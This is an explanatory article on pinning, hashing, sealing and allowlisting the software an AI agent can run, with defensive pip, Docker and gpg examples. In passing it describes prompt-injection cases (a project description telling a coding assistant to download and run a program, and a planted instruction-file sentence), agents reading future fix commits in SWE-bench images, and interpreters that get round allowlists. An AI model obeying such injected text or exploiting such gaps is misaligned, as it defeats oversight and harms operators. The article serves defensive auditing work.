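# Freezing and auditing the software an AI agent can reach before deployment

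## What can be fixed in advance, and what an audit of it can show

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by calling software tools in a loop. A coding agent reads files, runs tests and edits source code until a bug is gone. It acts through software that other people wrote: the operating system, the packages a project depends on, the add-ons a user has chosen and the services reached over a network. Organisations that deploy agents can freeze much of this software beforehand by inspecting it, recording the exact versions, storing the result and having the computer block anything else. The agent then works with the same programs that the auditors examined.

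The technique is older than AI agents and comes from the general practice of securing software supply chains. Agents complicate it because they can install programs on their own while they work, and because part of what determines their behaviour, usually including the model, runs on machines the operator does not control.

### The software behind one bug fix

*How Claude Code works*, Anthropic's guide to its coding agent, uses the request "fix the failing tests" as an example. The agent runs the test suite, reads the error output, searches for the relevant source files, reads and edits them, and runs the tests again. The model itself only produces text. In Anthropic's turn-by-turn account of a similar request, the model first outputs a call to run `npm test`. A separate program, the harness, then runs the command and adds the result to the text that the model receives next. *Components of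 A Coding Agent*, by the machine-learning writer Raschka, similarly describes a coding harness as the software scaffold around a model.

A single request to an agent can start several programs. In *Coding agent fundamentals*, a set of lecture slides from UT Austin, a user asks an agent to fix the handling of empty search queries, and the operating system starts six processes: a text search, a comparison of file versions, a style check, a type check and two test runs. The style check starts through `uvx`, which downloads a Python tool if the machine has no copy of it. Even this small repair may therefore involve runtime installation, the adding of software after the agent has started work.

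An agent's software stack is everything the agent can execute or call. For Claude Code, that covers any command the user could type, including package managers. The table divides the stack by who can change each part.

| Layer | Its part in the bug fix | Who changes it | When |
|---|---|---|---|
| Base system | Kernel, command shell, version control | Distribution maintainers publish; the administrator installs | At system upgrades |
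| Language packages | Test runner, libraries the project imports | Package authors publish; developers or the agent install | At any install command |
| Harness | Runs the model and its tool calls | The harness vendor, or an administrator | Often in the background |
| Plugins | Extra commands and instructions | Plugin authors, marketplace owners, the user's employer | Often at the start of a session |
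| Tool servers | Access to a bug tracker, for example | Whoever runs the server | At any time, if the server is remote |
| Remote services | Code hosts, package downloads, web pages | Their owners | At any time |
| Model | Produces the next command | The model vendor, or an operator who hosts the model | At a new release, or behind an unchanged name |

Language packages mostly come from a package registry, a public server such as PyPI for Python or npm for JavaScript. Some operators run a mirror, which is their own server that stores or relays the registry's packages. A plugin is an add-on that gives an agent new instructions, scripts or tools. A skill is a smaller add-on, typically a set of instructions that the model loads when a task needs them. An MCP server is a program that offers tools to agents through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard, and it may run on the user's machine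 or on someone else's.

The harness may change more often than many users realise. According to Anthropic's installation guide, the standard version of Claude Code checks for updates at start-up and periodically while it runs, installs them in the background and switches to them at the next start. An administrator who wants one fixed version can set `DISABLE_UPDATES`, which blocks both background and manual updates. `DISABLE_AUTOUPDATER` stops only the background check, so users can still update by hand. `minimumVersion` sets the oldest version allowed but permits every later release. Two further settings prevent the program from starting if its version is outside a given range.

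Plugins have their own update rules. Anthropic turns automatic updates on by default for most of its official plugin marketplaces and off for third-party ones. A running session keeps the versions it has loaded, and the next session loads the new ones. Plugins that a user or employer has switched on in a Claude account also arrive automatically, and installing a plugin also installs any others it depends on. Since August 2026, administrators of Copilot, GitHub's coding assistant, have been able to turn on automatic updates for individual marketplaces on their organisation's allowlist, which lists the only marketplaces it permits (GitHub, *Enterprise-managed settings now support autoUpdate for plugin marketplaces*, 2026). The allowlist fixes where the plugins come from, but their contents can still change.

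Changing only the harness can considerably alter an agent's work. UT Austin cites a test by LangChain, a company that makes agent frameworks, on Terminal-Bench 2.0, a benchmark of 89 command-line tasks. Re-engineering the harness while keeping the same model raised the score from 52.8 to 66.5. This is a vendor's result for its own product, but a second case supports the same conclusion. Anthropic's *An update on recent Claude Code quality reports* traces a run of user complaints in March and April 2026 to three changes in its products. The company had lowered the default amount of reasoning, introduced a bug that discarded the model's earlier reasoning at every turn in some sessions, and added an instruction to keep answers short, which lowered performance on one evaluation by 3%. The software developer Willison (2026) also concluded that the models were not to blame. Programs that called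 the models directly, without the harness, were unaffected, so an audit of the model alone would have missed all three changes.

### Three questions for an audit

An auditor of the software an agent can reach needs to find out what it includes, where each component came from, and whether the components now running are the ones that were approved. Each question requires separate tools, and answering one does not answer the other two.

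To identify the contents, auditors use a software bill of materials (SBOM), a machine-readable inventory of the components in a piece of software. A lockfile is a narrower list that gives the exact version, and usually the hash, of every package in a project, including those that other packages depend on. A Python project's lockfile normally omits the shell, the version-control program and the harness, so an auditor who reads only that file sees only a fraction of the software the bug fix used. Both kinds of list can also go out of date.

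Provenance is a signed record of the source and build process that produced a piece of software. The signature lets a reader check who issued the record, but not whether the issuer told the truth. If the build is reproducible, meaning that anyone who repeats it from the same source gets identical bytes, outsiders can test the record by building the program themselves.

To check what is running, an auditor needs a hash, or digest, which is a short value computed from a file's contents that in practice changes whenever the contents do. A pin is a recorded choice of one exact version, by version number or by hash. A version number is a label the publisher attaches, so someone who pins by number relies on the registry to keep serving the same bytes under it. Pinning by hash removes that reliance if the installing program compares the hash and stops when it differs. *Inside the Scaffold* (Rombaut,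 2026) also uses pins. It compares the source code of 13 coding agents at recorded commit hashes, which identify exact states of a code repository, so readers can inspect the same code after the projects change.

Users of Claude Code can check a release's origin and its identity separately. For each release, Anthropic publishes a manifest, a file with the hashes of the program for every supported platform, and since version 2.1.89 it has signed the manifest with its own key. A user first confirms that the key belongs to Anthropic and checks the signature, which establishes that Anthropic issued the manifest. The user then computes the hash of the installed program and compares it with the one in the manifest. A match establishes that this copy is the one Anthropic released. Neither step shows which source code went into the program; a user would need a provenance record of the build for that.

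Operators can check many files at once by putting them into an image, a stored file system from which identical containers or virtual machines start. A container is a group of processes that the operating system confines to their own file system. In the most common arrangement for running an agent's code, according to *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026), each task gets a fresh container from a known image, and the system destroys the container afterwards. A sealed image also has all its software installed beforehand and allows no installation while the agent works, so one digest identifies the whole collection.

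A container's image does not include the kernel, the core of the operating system. Containers share the kernel of the machine they run on, as *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026) points out, and a single flaw in it can let a program escape. An administrator can also upgrade that kernel without changing the image's digest. The paper recommends stronger separation for agents that execute generated code. One option is gVisor, which handles the container's requests in a substitute kernel. Another is Kata Containers, which gives each group of containers a small virtual machine with its own kernel. When the machine belongs to someone else, a correct recorded digest does not prove what runs there. The operator would need remote attestation, a hardware-signed statement of which software the machine has started.

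### The guarantee and how it fails

Let A be the set of file hashes approved at the audit. What a fixed stack is meant to guarantee is the following:

*Every program file executed before the next audit has a hash in A.*

In symbols, let h(f, t) be the hash of file f at time t. Then h(f, t) ∈ A for every program file f that the computer executes at any time t between the two audits. The condition includes t because a check at installation does not cover a file that someone alters an hour later.

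What the software does at a given moment depends on which program files run and on everything those programs read. If the agent's software does something after the audit that it could not have done at the time of the audit, there are therefore three possible explanations. If a program ran whose hash is outside A, someone has either added it where there was no program before or replaced an approved program with it. If only approved programs ran, the new behaviour must come from a change in what they read outside the approved files.

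Installing software at runtime ordinarily adds files. If `uvx` fetches a style checker that was not in the audited stack, the guarantee fails as soon as the checker runs, even if the checker is harmless. Destroying the container after each task doesn't stop the added program from running during the session, but it does limit how long the program remains, which is one reason *Containing the Autonomous Operator* recommends a new sandbox for each session.

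An update replaces the program that a command runs. On macOS and Linux, for example, the command that starts Claude Code is a link to one of several version directories, so after a background update the same command runs different code. The new release may well be better, and it may fix a security flaw, but the auditors have not seen it.

Behaviour that comes from outside is harder to deal with, because it can occur while every hash is in A. The plainest case is a hosted model. *DreamBench-SWE* (2026), a benchmark of how software agents manage their memory over several sessions, used three tests to confirm that the agent's container could not see the harness's code or the reference solutions. The container still had a network connection, because the agent had to reach its model, gpt-5.5, on the vendor's servers. The name of a hosted model may also be an alias that the vendor can point at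 a different model, so *DreamBench-SWE* cautions that others may be unable to reproduce the behaviour exactly even with the harness pinned. Remote tool servers raise the same difficulty. Under the July 2026 revision of the Model Context Protocol (2026), the list of tools a server offers no longer varies between connections, but the server's owner can still change the programs behind those tools. Outside behaviour can also come from text, such as a web page or an instruction file on the local disk, or from a script that the agent writes for an approved interpreter to run.

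*SoK* (Dehghantanha and Homayoun, 2026), a survey of attacks on agents, draws nearly the same distinction between two kinds of attacker. A supply-chain attacker publishes a doctored package or plugin, which has to reach the agent's machine as a file. An attacker who takes over an outside service can feed the agent false results without changing any local file. One of the survey's scenarios combines outside text with an added file. A user asks a coding assistant to find and set up a popular Python project, the project's description tells the AI to download and run a program, and the agent complies. A computer that refused to run files outside the approved set A would stop the downloaded program. It would not stop the agent from following an instruction that needs only approved programs, such as one to delete files or send data elsewhere.

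Even where the guarantee holds without exception, a file's membership of A shows that it is the one the auditors approved, not that it is harmless. Their approval is only as reliable as their examination, and even repeated examination can miss a bug. According to Anthropic, the bug that discarded Claude's earlier reasoning passed several human and automated code reviews as well as unit and end-to-end tests, and engineers needed more than a week to find the cause. When the company later ran its automated reviewer on the faulty changes, Claude Opus 4.7 found the bug once it had the related code repositories, and Opus 4.6 did not. Anthropic had begun to sign its manifests before it fixed the bug in version 2.1.101, so a user who checked one of the last faulty releases would have found a valid signature and a matching hash. A flaw hidden on purpose would presumably be harder to spot than this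 accidental one. An approved file's hash also remains in A if researchers discover a vulnerability in the file after the audit.

### Isolation in current agent frameworks

How much of this an operator can enforce depends partly on the harness. Wei (2026), in *Architectural Design Decisions in AI Agent Harnesses*, surveyed 70 publicly available agent projects and recorded how each one isolates the agent's commands from the rest of the machine. Of these projects, 17% had no isolation, 45% used a separate process on the same machine, 31% used containers, and 7% used WebAssembly, a format for running compiled code inside a restricted virtual machine.

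The list of projects closed on 23 March 2026. The source code was open for 67 of them, and the other three entries are based on public technical material. AI agents helped search and read the code under a fixed protocol. Human researchers made the final judgments and re-examined 15 projects, with 94% agreement before discussion. The percentages are best treated as rough proportions, because the survey is a single-author preprint, counts little-used and popular projects equally, and allowed the largest code bases to be sampled rather than read in full.

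In 62% of the projects Wei studied, the agent runs with no isolation or only in a separate process, and the framework supplies no image that an operator could seal. The agent's commands use whatever software is installed on the host machine, so an operator who wants a fixed stack has to build a container or virtual machine around the harness. Another 31% use containers, which come closer to a fixed stack, but a container with network access and a working package manager can still install new software. Wei also found that 40% of the projects kept no log of security events, 35% kept only basic text logs, and 5% kept logs designed to reveal tampering. With most of these frameworks, an operator who wanted to show afterwards which programs had run would have to collect the evidence by other means.

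## Building a sealed image offline and checking it

An invented example illustrates how to seal an image. An agent analyses spreadsheets for a finance department, and its scripts use three Python packages directly: pandas for tables, openpyxl for Excel files and matplotlib for charts. These bring in about a dozen others, such as numpy for arithmetic and pillow for images. The additional packages run with the same permissions as the rest of the code, even though the developers never chose them by name.

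### Locking, downloading and reviewing the packages

The developers write the three names into a file called `requirements.in`. A resolver then selects one version of every package the agent needs, including the indirect ones. pip's *Repeatable Installs*, a guide to Python's standard package installer, recommends the add-on pip-tools for generating such lists:

```
pip-compile --generate-hashes --output-file requirements.txt requirements.in
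```

The resulting lockfile has an entry of this form for each package:

```
openpyxl==3.1.5 \
    --hash=sha256:<hash of the wheel> \
    --hash=sha256:<hash of the source archive>
```

The entry has two hashes because the publisher offers this version both as a wheel (a ready-built package) and as source code. A package with compiled parts often has many more, one for each combination of operating system, processor and Python version. An entry therefore allows any one of several files.

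pip also has its own command, `pip lock`, which writes a file named `pylock.toml`. The pip reference marks it as experimental and guarantees the file only for the Python version and platform that produced it. When Willison (2026) locked two packages with it, the result ran to 519 lines. He also describes the option `--uploaded-prior-to`, which ignores recent uploads: with the value `P3D`, pip considers only files at least three days old. The delay gives other people time to notice a bad release.

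Next, a connected machine downloads the files into a directory, conventionally called a wheelhouse:

```
python -m pip download --require-hashes --only-binary :all: \
    --dest wheelhouse -r requirements.txt
```

This machine should have the same Python version and platform as the image, since pip otherwise selects wheels for the wrong system. If they differ, the operator can specify the image's version and platform with `--python-version` and `--platform`. The pip manual lists functions that return the right values for these options.

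pip's *Secure installs* gives the rules for `--require-hashes`. Every requirement needs an exact version and a hash, and so does every indirect dependency. If one is missing, pip stops with an error, because an attacker could otherwise use the single unhashed entry. The hashes must also come from the operator's own file. PyPI attaches a hash to each download link, but anyone who controlled the server could change the file and its hash together, so pip relies on that hash only to detect damaged downloads. The second option, `--only-binary :all:`, refuses source archives. Building a package from source can run code supplied by its author, and at this stage nobody has reviewed that code.

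An auditor should read the installation command as well as the lockfile. Since version 26.2, pip has had a `--no-require-hashes` option that checks packages with a hash and accepts the rest unchecked. The strict mode, which requires a hash for every package, still accepts old-style links that end in an MD5 hash, although pip rejects MD5 elsewhere as too weak. A build script that calls a project's `setup.py` directly bypasses pip and downloads missing dependencies without any check.

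The reviewers now have about fifteen files. A wheel is a zip archive, so they can unpack it, read the Python code and look for anything unexpected, such as a chart library that opens network connections. They can also look up each version in a database of known vulnerabilities. Much of numpy and pillow is compiled machine code, which is far harder to read, so most reviewers rely on the publisher for those parts. The lock then restricts the project to the files they reviewed, but it will still allow a malicious file that they failed to recognise.

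Locking every package is stricter than pinning only the main tools. *BLACKICE* (Kaplan, Warnecke and Archibald, 2025) describes a container image from the software company Databricks that bundles 14 programs for testing the security of AI models. Its Dockerfile, the text file of instructions Docker follows to build the image, lists each tool at the top with a pinned version number or Git commit. Many of the tools have conflicting requirements, so most get their own Python environment. The rest share one, and a file called `global_requirements.txt` resolves their conflicts.

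Pinning a tool's version does not fix the versions of the libraries it depends on. If a pinned tool requires version 2 or later of some library, pip installs the newest version available on the day of the build, unless another list restricts the choice. Two teams that build from such a recipe a month apart may therefore get the same tools with different libraries, but if they download the finished BlackIce image by its digest, they get the same bytes.

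### Building and starting the image

The operator carries the wheelhouse, the lockfile and the agent's own scripts to a machine with no internet connection. The base image, which supplies Debian Linux and Python, goes into a registry on the same closed network, here called `registry.internal`. The Dockerfile refers to the base image by digest because the publisher points a name such as `python:3.13-slim` at a new image whenever there is an update.

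```
FROM registry.internal/python@sha256:<digest of the base image>
ENV PYTHONDONTWRITEBYTECODE=1
RUN --mount=type=bind,target=/src \
    python -m pip install --no-index --find-links=/src/wheelhouse \
    --require-hashes --no-deps --only-binary :all: \
    --no-cache-dir --no-compile -r /src/requirements.txt
COPY agent/ /opt/agent/
USER 1000
CMD ["sleep", "infinity"]
```

With `--no-index`, pip ignores package registries and looks only in the wheelhouse, where `--find-links` points. The guide *Use “pip install” safely* recommends using the next three options together. One of them, `--no-deps`, stops pip from installing anything the lockfile does not name. The download command deliberately omits this option so that a forgotten dependency causes an error while the operator can still fetch it.

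If someone replaces the pillow wheel on the disk during the transfer, pip finds no match for the new file's hash in `requirements.txt` and stops, so the build produces no image. If someone adds a sixteenth wheel instead, pip does not install it because no requirement names it. The example in pip's guide to repeatable installs would install the extra wheel, because it passes every file in the wheelhouse to the installer, but according to the guide, hash checking also works with a wheelhouse.

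The operator then builds the image and sends it to the internal registry:

```
docker buildx build --no-cache --network=none --provenance=false \
    --build-arg SOURCE_DATE_EPOCH=$(git log -1 --pretty=%ct) \
    --metadata-file build.json \
    --output type=image,name=registry.internal/sheet-agent:1,push=true,rewrite-timestamp=true .
```

`--network=none` blocks network access for commands inside the build, so a script that tries to download something fails. `SOURCE_DATE_EPOCH` and `rewrite-timestamp` replace the time of the build with the date of the last source commit. `--provenance=false` stops Docker from attaching a build record, which would contain the actual time and change the overall digest. Docker writes the new digest to `build.json`.

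Four more commands produce the inventory and the signature. In them, `$IMAGE` stands for the image's name followed by its digest.

```
trivy image --format cyclonedx --output sbom.json "$IMAGE"
find agent -type f -exec sha256sum {} + > agent-files.txt
{ echo "$IMAGE"; sha256sum requirements.txt sbom.json agent-files.txt; } > release.txt
gpg --armor --detach-sign release.txt
```

Trivy is an open-source scanner that lists the packages in an image, and CycloneDX is a common format for an SBOM. The second command hashes the agent's own files. The signed file `release.txt` ties the image, the lockfile and both inventories together, so nobody can later replace one of them without invalidating the signature or causing a hash mismatch.

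On the machine where the agent will work, the operator checks the signature with `gpg --verify release.txt.asc release.txt` and starts the container:

```
docker run --detach --name job17 --network none --read-only \
    --tmpfs /tmp:rw,noexec,nosuid,size=256m \
    --cap-drop ALL --security-opt no-new-privileges \
    --mount type=bind,source=/srv/job17/in,target=/data/in,readonly \
    --mount type=bind,source=/srv/job17/out,target=/data/out \
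    "$IMAGE"
```

The container has no network, and its programs cannot alter the files that came with the image. They can write only to `/tmp` and an output folder. The `noexec` setting stops the agent from directly running program files saved in `/tmp`. The output folder needs the same protection, which the operator can provide by placing it on a host disk mounted with `noexec`. Python is an approved program, so it can still run scripts saved in either place.

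An agent with no network access cannot reach a hosted model, so in this design the harness runs outside the container and passes each command in with `docker exec`, for example `docker exec job17 python /opt/agent/summarise.py /data/in/sales.xlsx`. This keeps the harness connected to the model while the spreadsheet tools run offline. The image's digest does not cover the harness, so the operator has to pin and check the harness separately.

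### What the inventory leaves out

An SBOM for the spreadsheet image lists the Python packages and dozens of Debian packages that came with the base image. Auditors can compare the Python entries with the lockfile. Any entry found only in the SBOM needs an explanation, except pip, which the base image supplies. Auditors can also search the SBOM whenever researchers announce a new vulnerability, which becomes more important as the image ages.

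The scanner builds its package list mainly from records that package managers leave behind. Malka, Zacchiroli and Zimmermann (2026), in *Docker Does Not Guarantee Reproducibility*, ran Trivy on 1,116 pairs of images, each an original and its rebuilt copy. For 20 pairs (less than 2%), it found no package list or exceeded a 25-minute limit. Some projects delete the records to make their images smaller, although the programs remain. The failure rate is low, but someone could delete a package's record to hide it.

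A record also gives a package's name and version without confirming that the code is unchanged. In BlackIce, for example, users can put source-code changes into a `patches` directory, and the build applies them to a tool before installing it. Kaplan and colleagues mention a change that lets a tester give the model under test extra security instructions. Unless the patch also changes the version number, the patched tool would have the same inventory entry as the original.

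A package inventory may omit files that were added without a package manager. BlackIce contains one such file, a script called `biasforge` that tests models for bias and is copied directly into the image. In the spreadsheet image, everything under `/opt/agent` is also added without a package manager. Suppose that directory contains three scripts, a table of exchange rates and a text file with instructions for formatting reports. A package inventory would omit all five. An outdated exchange rate would make the reports wrong, and someone could add a sentence to the text file telling the agent to leave certain accounts out. For this reason, `agent-files.txt` lists these files separately, and reviewers have to open each one.

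SWE-bench, a benchmark in which agents repair real bugs in open-source projects, supplies images of each project as it was before the repair. In September 2025, users reported on the benchmark's issue tracker that the Git history in some of these images also held later commits, which can include the repair itself, and that agents had used ordinary Git commands to look at them. Git was a legitimate part of the image, and an SBOM would have listed it correctly, but the fault was in the data. An auditor could have found it by running `git log --all` and comparing the commit dates with the date of the bug.

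### Rebuilding the image and comparing digests

An auditor may also want to know whether the image came from the files the reviewers read. A compromised build machine could add a program after the review, and the operator would sign the altered image without knowing it had changed. To test for this, a second team rebuilds the image from the same base image, lockfile, wheelhouse and scripts on a separate machine. If the two digests match, an attacker would have had to tamper with both machines in the same way to add a program.

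The test is strict because of how Docker computes the digest. An image consists of layers, and each layer is an archive of the files that one instruction added or changed. A short file called the manifest lists the hash of every layer and of the image's configuration. With H for the hash function, C for the configuration and L₁ to Lₙ for the layers,

digest = H(manifest), where the manifest contains H(C), H(L₁), …, H(Lₙ).

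Changing one byte in any layer changes that layer's hash, and therefore the manifest and the digest. The archive includes file dates, so two builds a minute apart differ unless the dates are held constant. Putting the same files in a different order also changes the archive.

*It's Not Just Timestamps* (Solarin, 2026) measured how often ordinary Dockerfiles produce the same digest when built twice with the same tools. The study sampled 2,000 actively maintained GitHub projects and could build an image for 1,123 of them. Only 30 of these (2.7%) gave matching digests. Another 209 (18.6%) matched once the dates were fixed with the two settings used in the spreadsheet example, and the remaining 884 (78.7%) still differed. Both builds ran on one platform, so these figures mostly exclude differences between machines, and an outside auditor would probably see fewer matches.

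Solarin analysed 954 detailed comparisons to find out what still differed after those settings. An image can have several causes at once.

| Cause | Share of comparisons | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Dates, ownership and other metadata | 100% | Date on an installed file |
| Formatting or file order | 78.1% | Sequence of entries in a directory listing |
| System logs | 43.3% | Log of Debian package installations |
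| Caches and databases | 36.8% | Index of installed fonts |
| Compiled files | 20.0% | Python bytecode |
| Files specific to the application | 13.0% | Generated report, downloaded model |
| Random data | 9.4% | Value drawn afresh in each build |
| Package-manager state | 5.6% | Record of installed packages |

The Dockerfile for the spreadsheet agent avoids several of these. It installs no Debian packages, so it writes no installation log, and `--no-cache-dir` keeps pip's cache out of the image. Python normally saves a partly translated form of scripts, called bytecode, so that they start faster, and bytecode contains a date by default. `PYTHONDONTWRITEBYTECODE` stops Python from saving it, and `--no-compile` stops pip from doing so. The two digests should match, but only a rebuild would confirm it.

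Many digest mismatches are harmless. Solarin rebuilt the official image for the Go programming language from its Dockerfile and got a digest that differed from the published one. Three of the five layers were identical, including the layer of about 60 megabytes that contains the Go tools. One of the other two came from an instruction that only creates a working directory, and it was 124 bytes in the rebuilt image and 126 in the published one. An auditor who sees only the two digests cannot tell a harmless mismatch from an attack and has to compare the layers file by file.

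Time makes the comparison much harder. Malka and colleagues (2026) collected 5,298 Docker builds that had succeeded on GitHub between July and October 2023 and repeated them less than two years later. Of these, 3,836 (72%) still produced an image. None of the images had the original digest, and none of the projects had set the dates to fixed values. The researchers therefore also compared file contents, ignoring dates, wherever they could still obtain the original image. All the files were identical in only 4 pairs of original and rebuilt images.

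They then compared package versions in the 1,096 pairs for which Trivy produced a list. All versions matched in 70 pairs, and in half of the pairs at least 22.6% of the packages had different versions. These differences are more serious than differences in dates, because different versions contain different code. An auditor who reads the Dockerfile today and rebuilds the image may be examining different software from what the original image contains.

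The same study found little benefit from standard advice on writing Dockerfiles. Malka and colleagues checked each file against rules such as "pin versions" and "delete temporary files". Compliance explained 27% of the variation in matching files and 12% of the variation in matching package versions. A few pinning rules were associated with slightly worse results, by less than three percentage points. The researchers suspect other influences, such as changes in the base image or the system's package manager. Pinning a few chosen packages would not prevent either change, so the weak result is not evidence against locking every package and the base image by hash.

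Much higher rates are possible with the package manager Nix. Each Nix package declares all its inputs, including the source code by hash, and Nix builds it in an isolated environment that contains only those inputs. In *Does Functional Package Management Enable Reproducible Builds at Scale?* (2025), Malka, Zacchiroli and Zimmermann rebuilt 709,816 packages from 17 snapshots, made between 2017 and 2023, of the Nixpkgs software collection. Over 99% still built. Apart from a drop in 2020, between 69% and 91% of the packages in each snapshot were bit-for-bit identical to the files that the project had originally distributed, with the highest rates in the latest snapshots.

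Python packages improved the most, from 27.64% identical in December 2017 to 98.28% in April 2023. The rate fell to 6.01% in June 2020, which the researchers traced to a pip update that changed how pip produced bytecode. Across the whole collection, build dates inside the files accounted for 14.8% of the mismatches the researchers analysed.

The Nix and Docker rates are not directly comparable, because Malka and colleagues counted single packages, and an image matches only if everything in it does. If an image contained fifteen packages, each with an independent 98.28% chance of matching, the probability that all fifteen matched would be 0.9828¹⁵, or about 77%. The pip update shows that failures can occur together. Malka and colleagues also took the build environment for each package from the Nix project's store of finished files, so they tested each package separately and did not rebuild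 the whole chain from source.

Rebuilding the spreadsheet image tests less than rebuilding a Nix package, because the image is built from finished wheels. Matching digests would show that the image contains the wheels in the lockfile, but not that the pillow wheel came from pillow's public source code. To establish that, someone would have to build the wheel from source and get the same bytes. Malka and colleagues propose that several independent parties build each package and publish signed hashes, so that an installer could require the hashes to match. They write that, with few exceptions, the infrastructure for this does not yet exist.

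### A record made at start-up

All these checks cover the image before it is used. Docker verifies an image's digest when downloading it, but does not hash every file again at each start. An operator may also start the right image with the wrong settings, for instance by leaving out `--network none`. Someone investigating an incident months later will want evidence of which image started and with what settings.

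Dehghantanha and Homayoun propose such evidence in the deployment checklist of their survey of attacks on agents. When the agent starts, the system tests whether its policy, input checks, isolation settings, logging and network rules are in place. It then sends a signed readiness record to the audit log. The record contains a hash of the policy, the list of tools and the decoding parameters, which control how the model chooses among possible next words. For the spreadsheet agent it might look like this, with the image digest and network setting added to the three items that the survey names:

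```
{
  "image": "sha256:<image digest>",
  "policy": "sha256:<hash of the policy file>",
  "tools": ["read_sheet", "run_python", "write_report"],
  "decoding": {"temperature": 0},
  "network": "none"
}
```

An auditor can compare the first line with the signed `release.txt` and the list of tools with the approved one. The second comparison would reveal an extra tool, such as `send_email`, even if the image were correct, because tools can also come from the harness. The survey also recommends keeping the log append-only and on another machine, so that the agent cannot edit its own history.

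The proposal is a single item in a checklist, and its value depends on who writes the record. If the harness writes it, an attacker who controls the harness can sign a false record. The operator can reduce this risk by having a separate program on the host read the digest and settings from Docker and sign the record with a key that the harness cannot reach. An attacker would then have to take over the host as well, which remote attestation by the hardware can help detect.

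## Lists of permitted programs, and the interpreter on the list

A signed digest identifies the approved image, but it does not stop a machine from running something else. Operating systems have a separate control to prevent that, known as application allowlisting or application control. Before a program file runs, the system checks it against a list of permitted programs and blocks it if there is no match. Antivirus software, by contrast, blocks only files it recognises as malicious.

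Companies used allowlists on staff computers long before there were AI agents. *Guide to Application Whitelisting* (Sedgewick, Souppaya and Scarfone, 2015), written for the National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), is the US government's standard introduction. It describes allowlisting as most practical on centrally managed machines that do the same work every day, such as a public kiosk that runs only a web browser. A container that analyses spreadsheets all day has a similarly regular workload.

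### How the system recognises a permitted program

A rule can identify a program by its location, publisher or hash. A path rule permits every file in a given folder. It needs no change when a program is updated, but anyone who can write to the folder can add a program. A publisher rule permits files with a valid signature from a named company. It also needs no change after an update, but it permits the company's other products and old versions of its software with known vulnerabilities. A hash rule permits one exact file, whatever its name or location. Every patch needs a new entry, and the vulnerable version can still run until an administrator deletes the old entry.

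Sedgewick and colleagues consider a combination of signatures and hashes the most accurate, but warn that it can be a heavy burden to maintain. To reduce this burden, many products let an administrator name a trusted updater and automatically add any file it installs to the list. On an audited machine, this option breaks the guarantee, because the set of approved hashes A grows without anyone examining the new files.

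The built-in system on Windows is App Control for Business, formerly Windows Defender Application Control (WDAC). According to Microsoft's *Essential Eight application control*, it applies deny rules before allow rules. If no rule matches, it can still allow a file that a designated installer put there or that Microsoft's reputation service rates as safe. An operator who wants a fixed list has to leave both options off. Microsoft recommends starting in audit mode, which lets unlisted programs run but logs them, and switching to enforcement once the log shows no unexpected entries.

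Linux can check approved files for changes using its Integrity Measurement Architecture (IMA), which a Python user describes in the forum post *Adding support for Linux IMA (Integrity Measurement Architecture)*. An administrator stores a signed hash alongside each approved file, and the kernel recomputes the hash and compares the two. If someone has altered the Python interpreter, for example, the kernel refuses to run it.

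The spreadsheet container from the previous section uses neither system, but its read-only image and `noexec` folders together amount to a path rule.

### Why an interpreter defeats the list

An interpreter is a program that reads instructions as text and carries them out. Python and the command shell are interpreters, and the spreadsheet image contains both. This leads to the main objection to freezing an agent's tools.

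When Python starts, the system checks that the interpreter is on the list of permitted programs, but it doesn't check the script that the interpreter runs. Python can express any computation that the machine has the memory and time to perform, so an agent that can choose its scripts freely can write any program the auditors left out. If the image has no tool for converting a spreadsheet to PDF, for example, the agent can write one. The list therefore doesn't limit what the agent can compute. Office workers rarely write their own replacement for a missing program, but a language model can do it in seconds.

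Microsoft's *Script enforcement with Windows Defender Application Control (WDAC)* warns that many Java and Python engines do not check the WDAC policy, so permitting one of these engines also permits every script it runs. Microsoft's *Security considerations for AppLocker* says that AppLocker, an older Windows allowlist, does not control what a program does after it starts. Sedgewick and colleagues note that products that claim to block a whole class of scripts generally block the interpreter.

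Other permitted programs can run code too, so removing Python and the shell is not enough. Microsoft publishes a list, compiled with outside security researchers, of programs that attackers can use to get round an allowlist. The version described in BornCity's *Windows Defender Application Control* (2022) includes build tools, shells and script hosts. Microsoft advises blocking every program on the list unless an organisation specifically needs it. The Canadian Centre for Cyber Security's *Microsoft recommended block rules* (2019) passed on similar advice. Australia's Essential Eight, a set of baseline security measures, requires Microsoft's blocklist at the top two of its three levels.

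These organisations therefore add a list of forbidden programs to their list of permitted ones. The forbidden list contains the cases people have found so far, and nobody can show that it is complete. An auditor of an agent's image has to check whether each program in it, not just the obvious interpreters, can run code that the agent supplies.

### Limits on what a script can affect

A script can calculate on its own, but it has to make a system call (a request to the kernel) to read a file, send data or start another program. The kernel applies the same permissions to Python whether the auditors or the agent wrote the script. An operator can therefore limit the effects of a program that nobody has seen.

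An agent in the spreadsheet container could write a program that searches for other machines, but the program would find none because the container has no network. The operator has placed no passwords or access keys in the container, and the start command limits where scripts can write. `--cap-drop ALL` removes an administrator's special privileges, and Docker's default filter blocks some system calls that ordinary programs seldom need.

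The start command still sets no limit on memory, processor time or the size of the output folder. A faulty loop could slow the whole host, which Docker's `--memory` and `--cpus` options would prevent. Confidential data can also leave despite `--network none`, because the harness sends the model whatever a script prints. If the model runs on a vendor's servers, a script that prints the payroll sends it to the vendor. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* lists this channel among the remaining risks in its own design, since the agent cannot work without its model.

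If the limits are tight, the objection is therefore correct about what the agent can compute but not about what it can affect. The limits can be tight for spreadsheet work because it needs so little access. An agent that deploys software needs a network connection and credentials, and any script it writes can use both.

### Four typed tools in place of a shell

One reply is to give the agent no way to supply code. The operator offers a few narrow tools whose arguments have declared types, such as a number or a file name from a fixed set, and the harness refuses any other call. Suppose a manager asks for total sales by region, with a chart. One agent has a single tool that runs any shell command. A second agent has these four:

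```
list_columns(file: "sales.xlsx" or "payroll.xlsx")
total_by(file: as above, group: a column, value: a numeric column)
bar_chart(total: the result of an earlier total_by call)
write_report(title: up to 80 characters, body: up to 5,000 characters)
```

The first agent would probably write a short pandas script, run it, fix any errors and save the result. The second would list the columns, call `total_by` with the region and sales columns, draw the chart and write the report. Both agents can complete the task in the same container, but an auditor can draw different conclusions about them.

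| Auditor's question | Agent with a shell | Agent with four typed tools |
|---|---|---|
| Which program files can run? | Any program in the image | The four tools and the programs they start |
| What can the agent compute? | Anything that memory and time allow | Column totals, and charts of them |
| Can the auditor test this beforehand? | Only by sampling | Every `total_by` call, but not every report text |
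| What can the model's vendor receive? | Any data in the input files | Column names and totals |
| Are the figures right? | The auditor has to read each script | Totals are as reliable as the tool; the report may misquote them |
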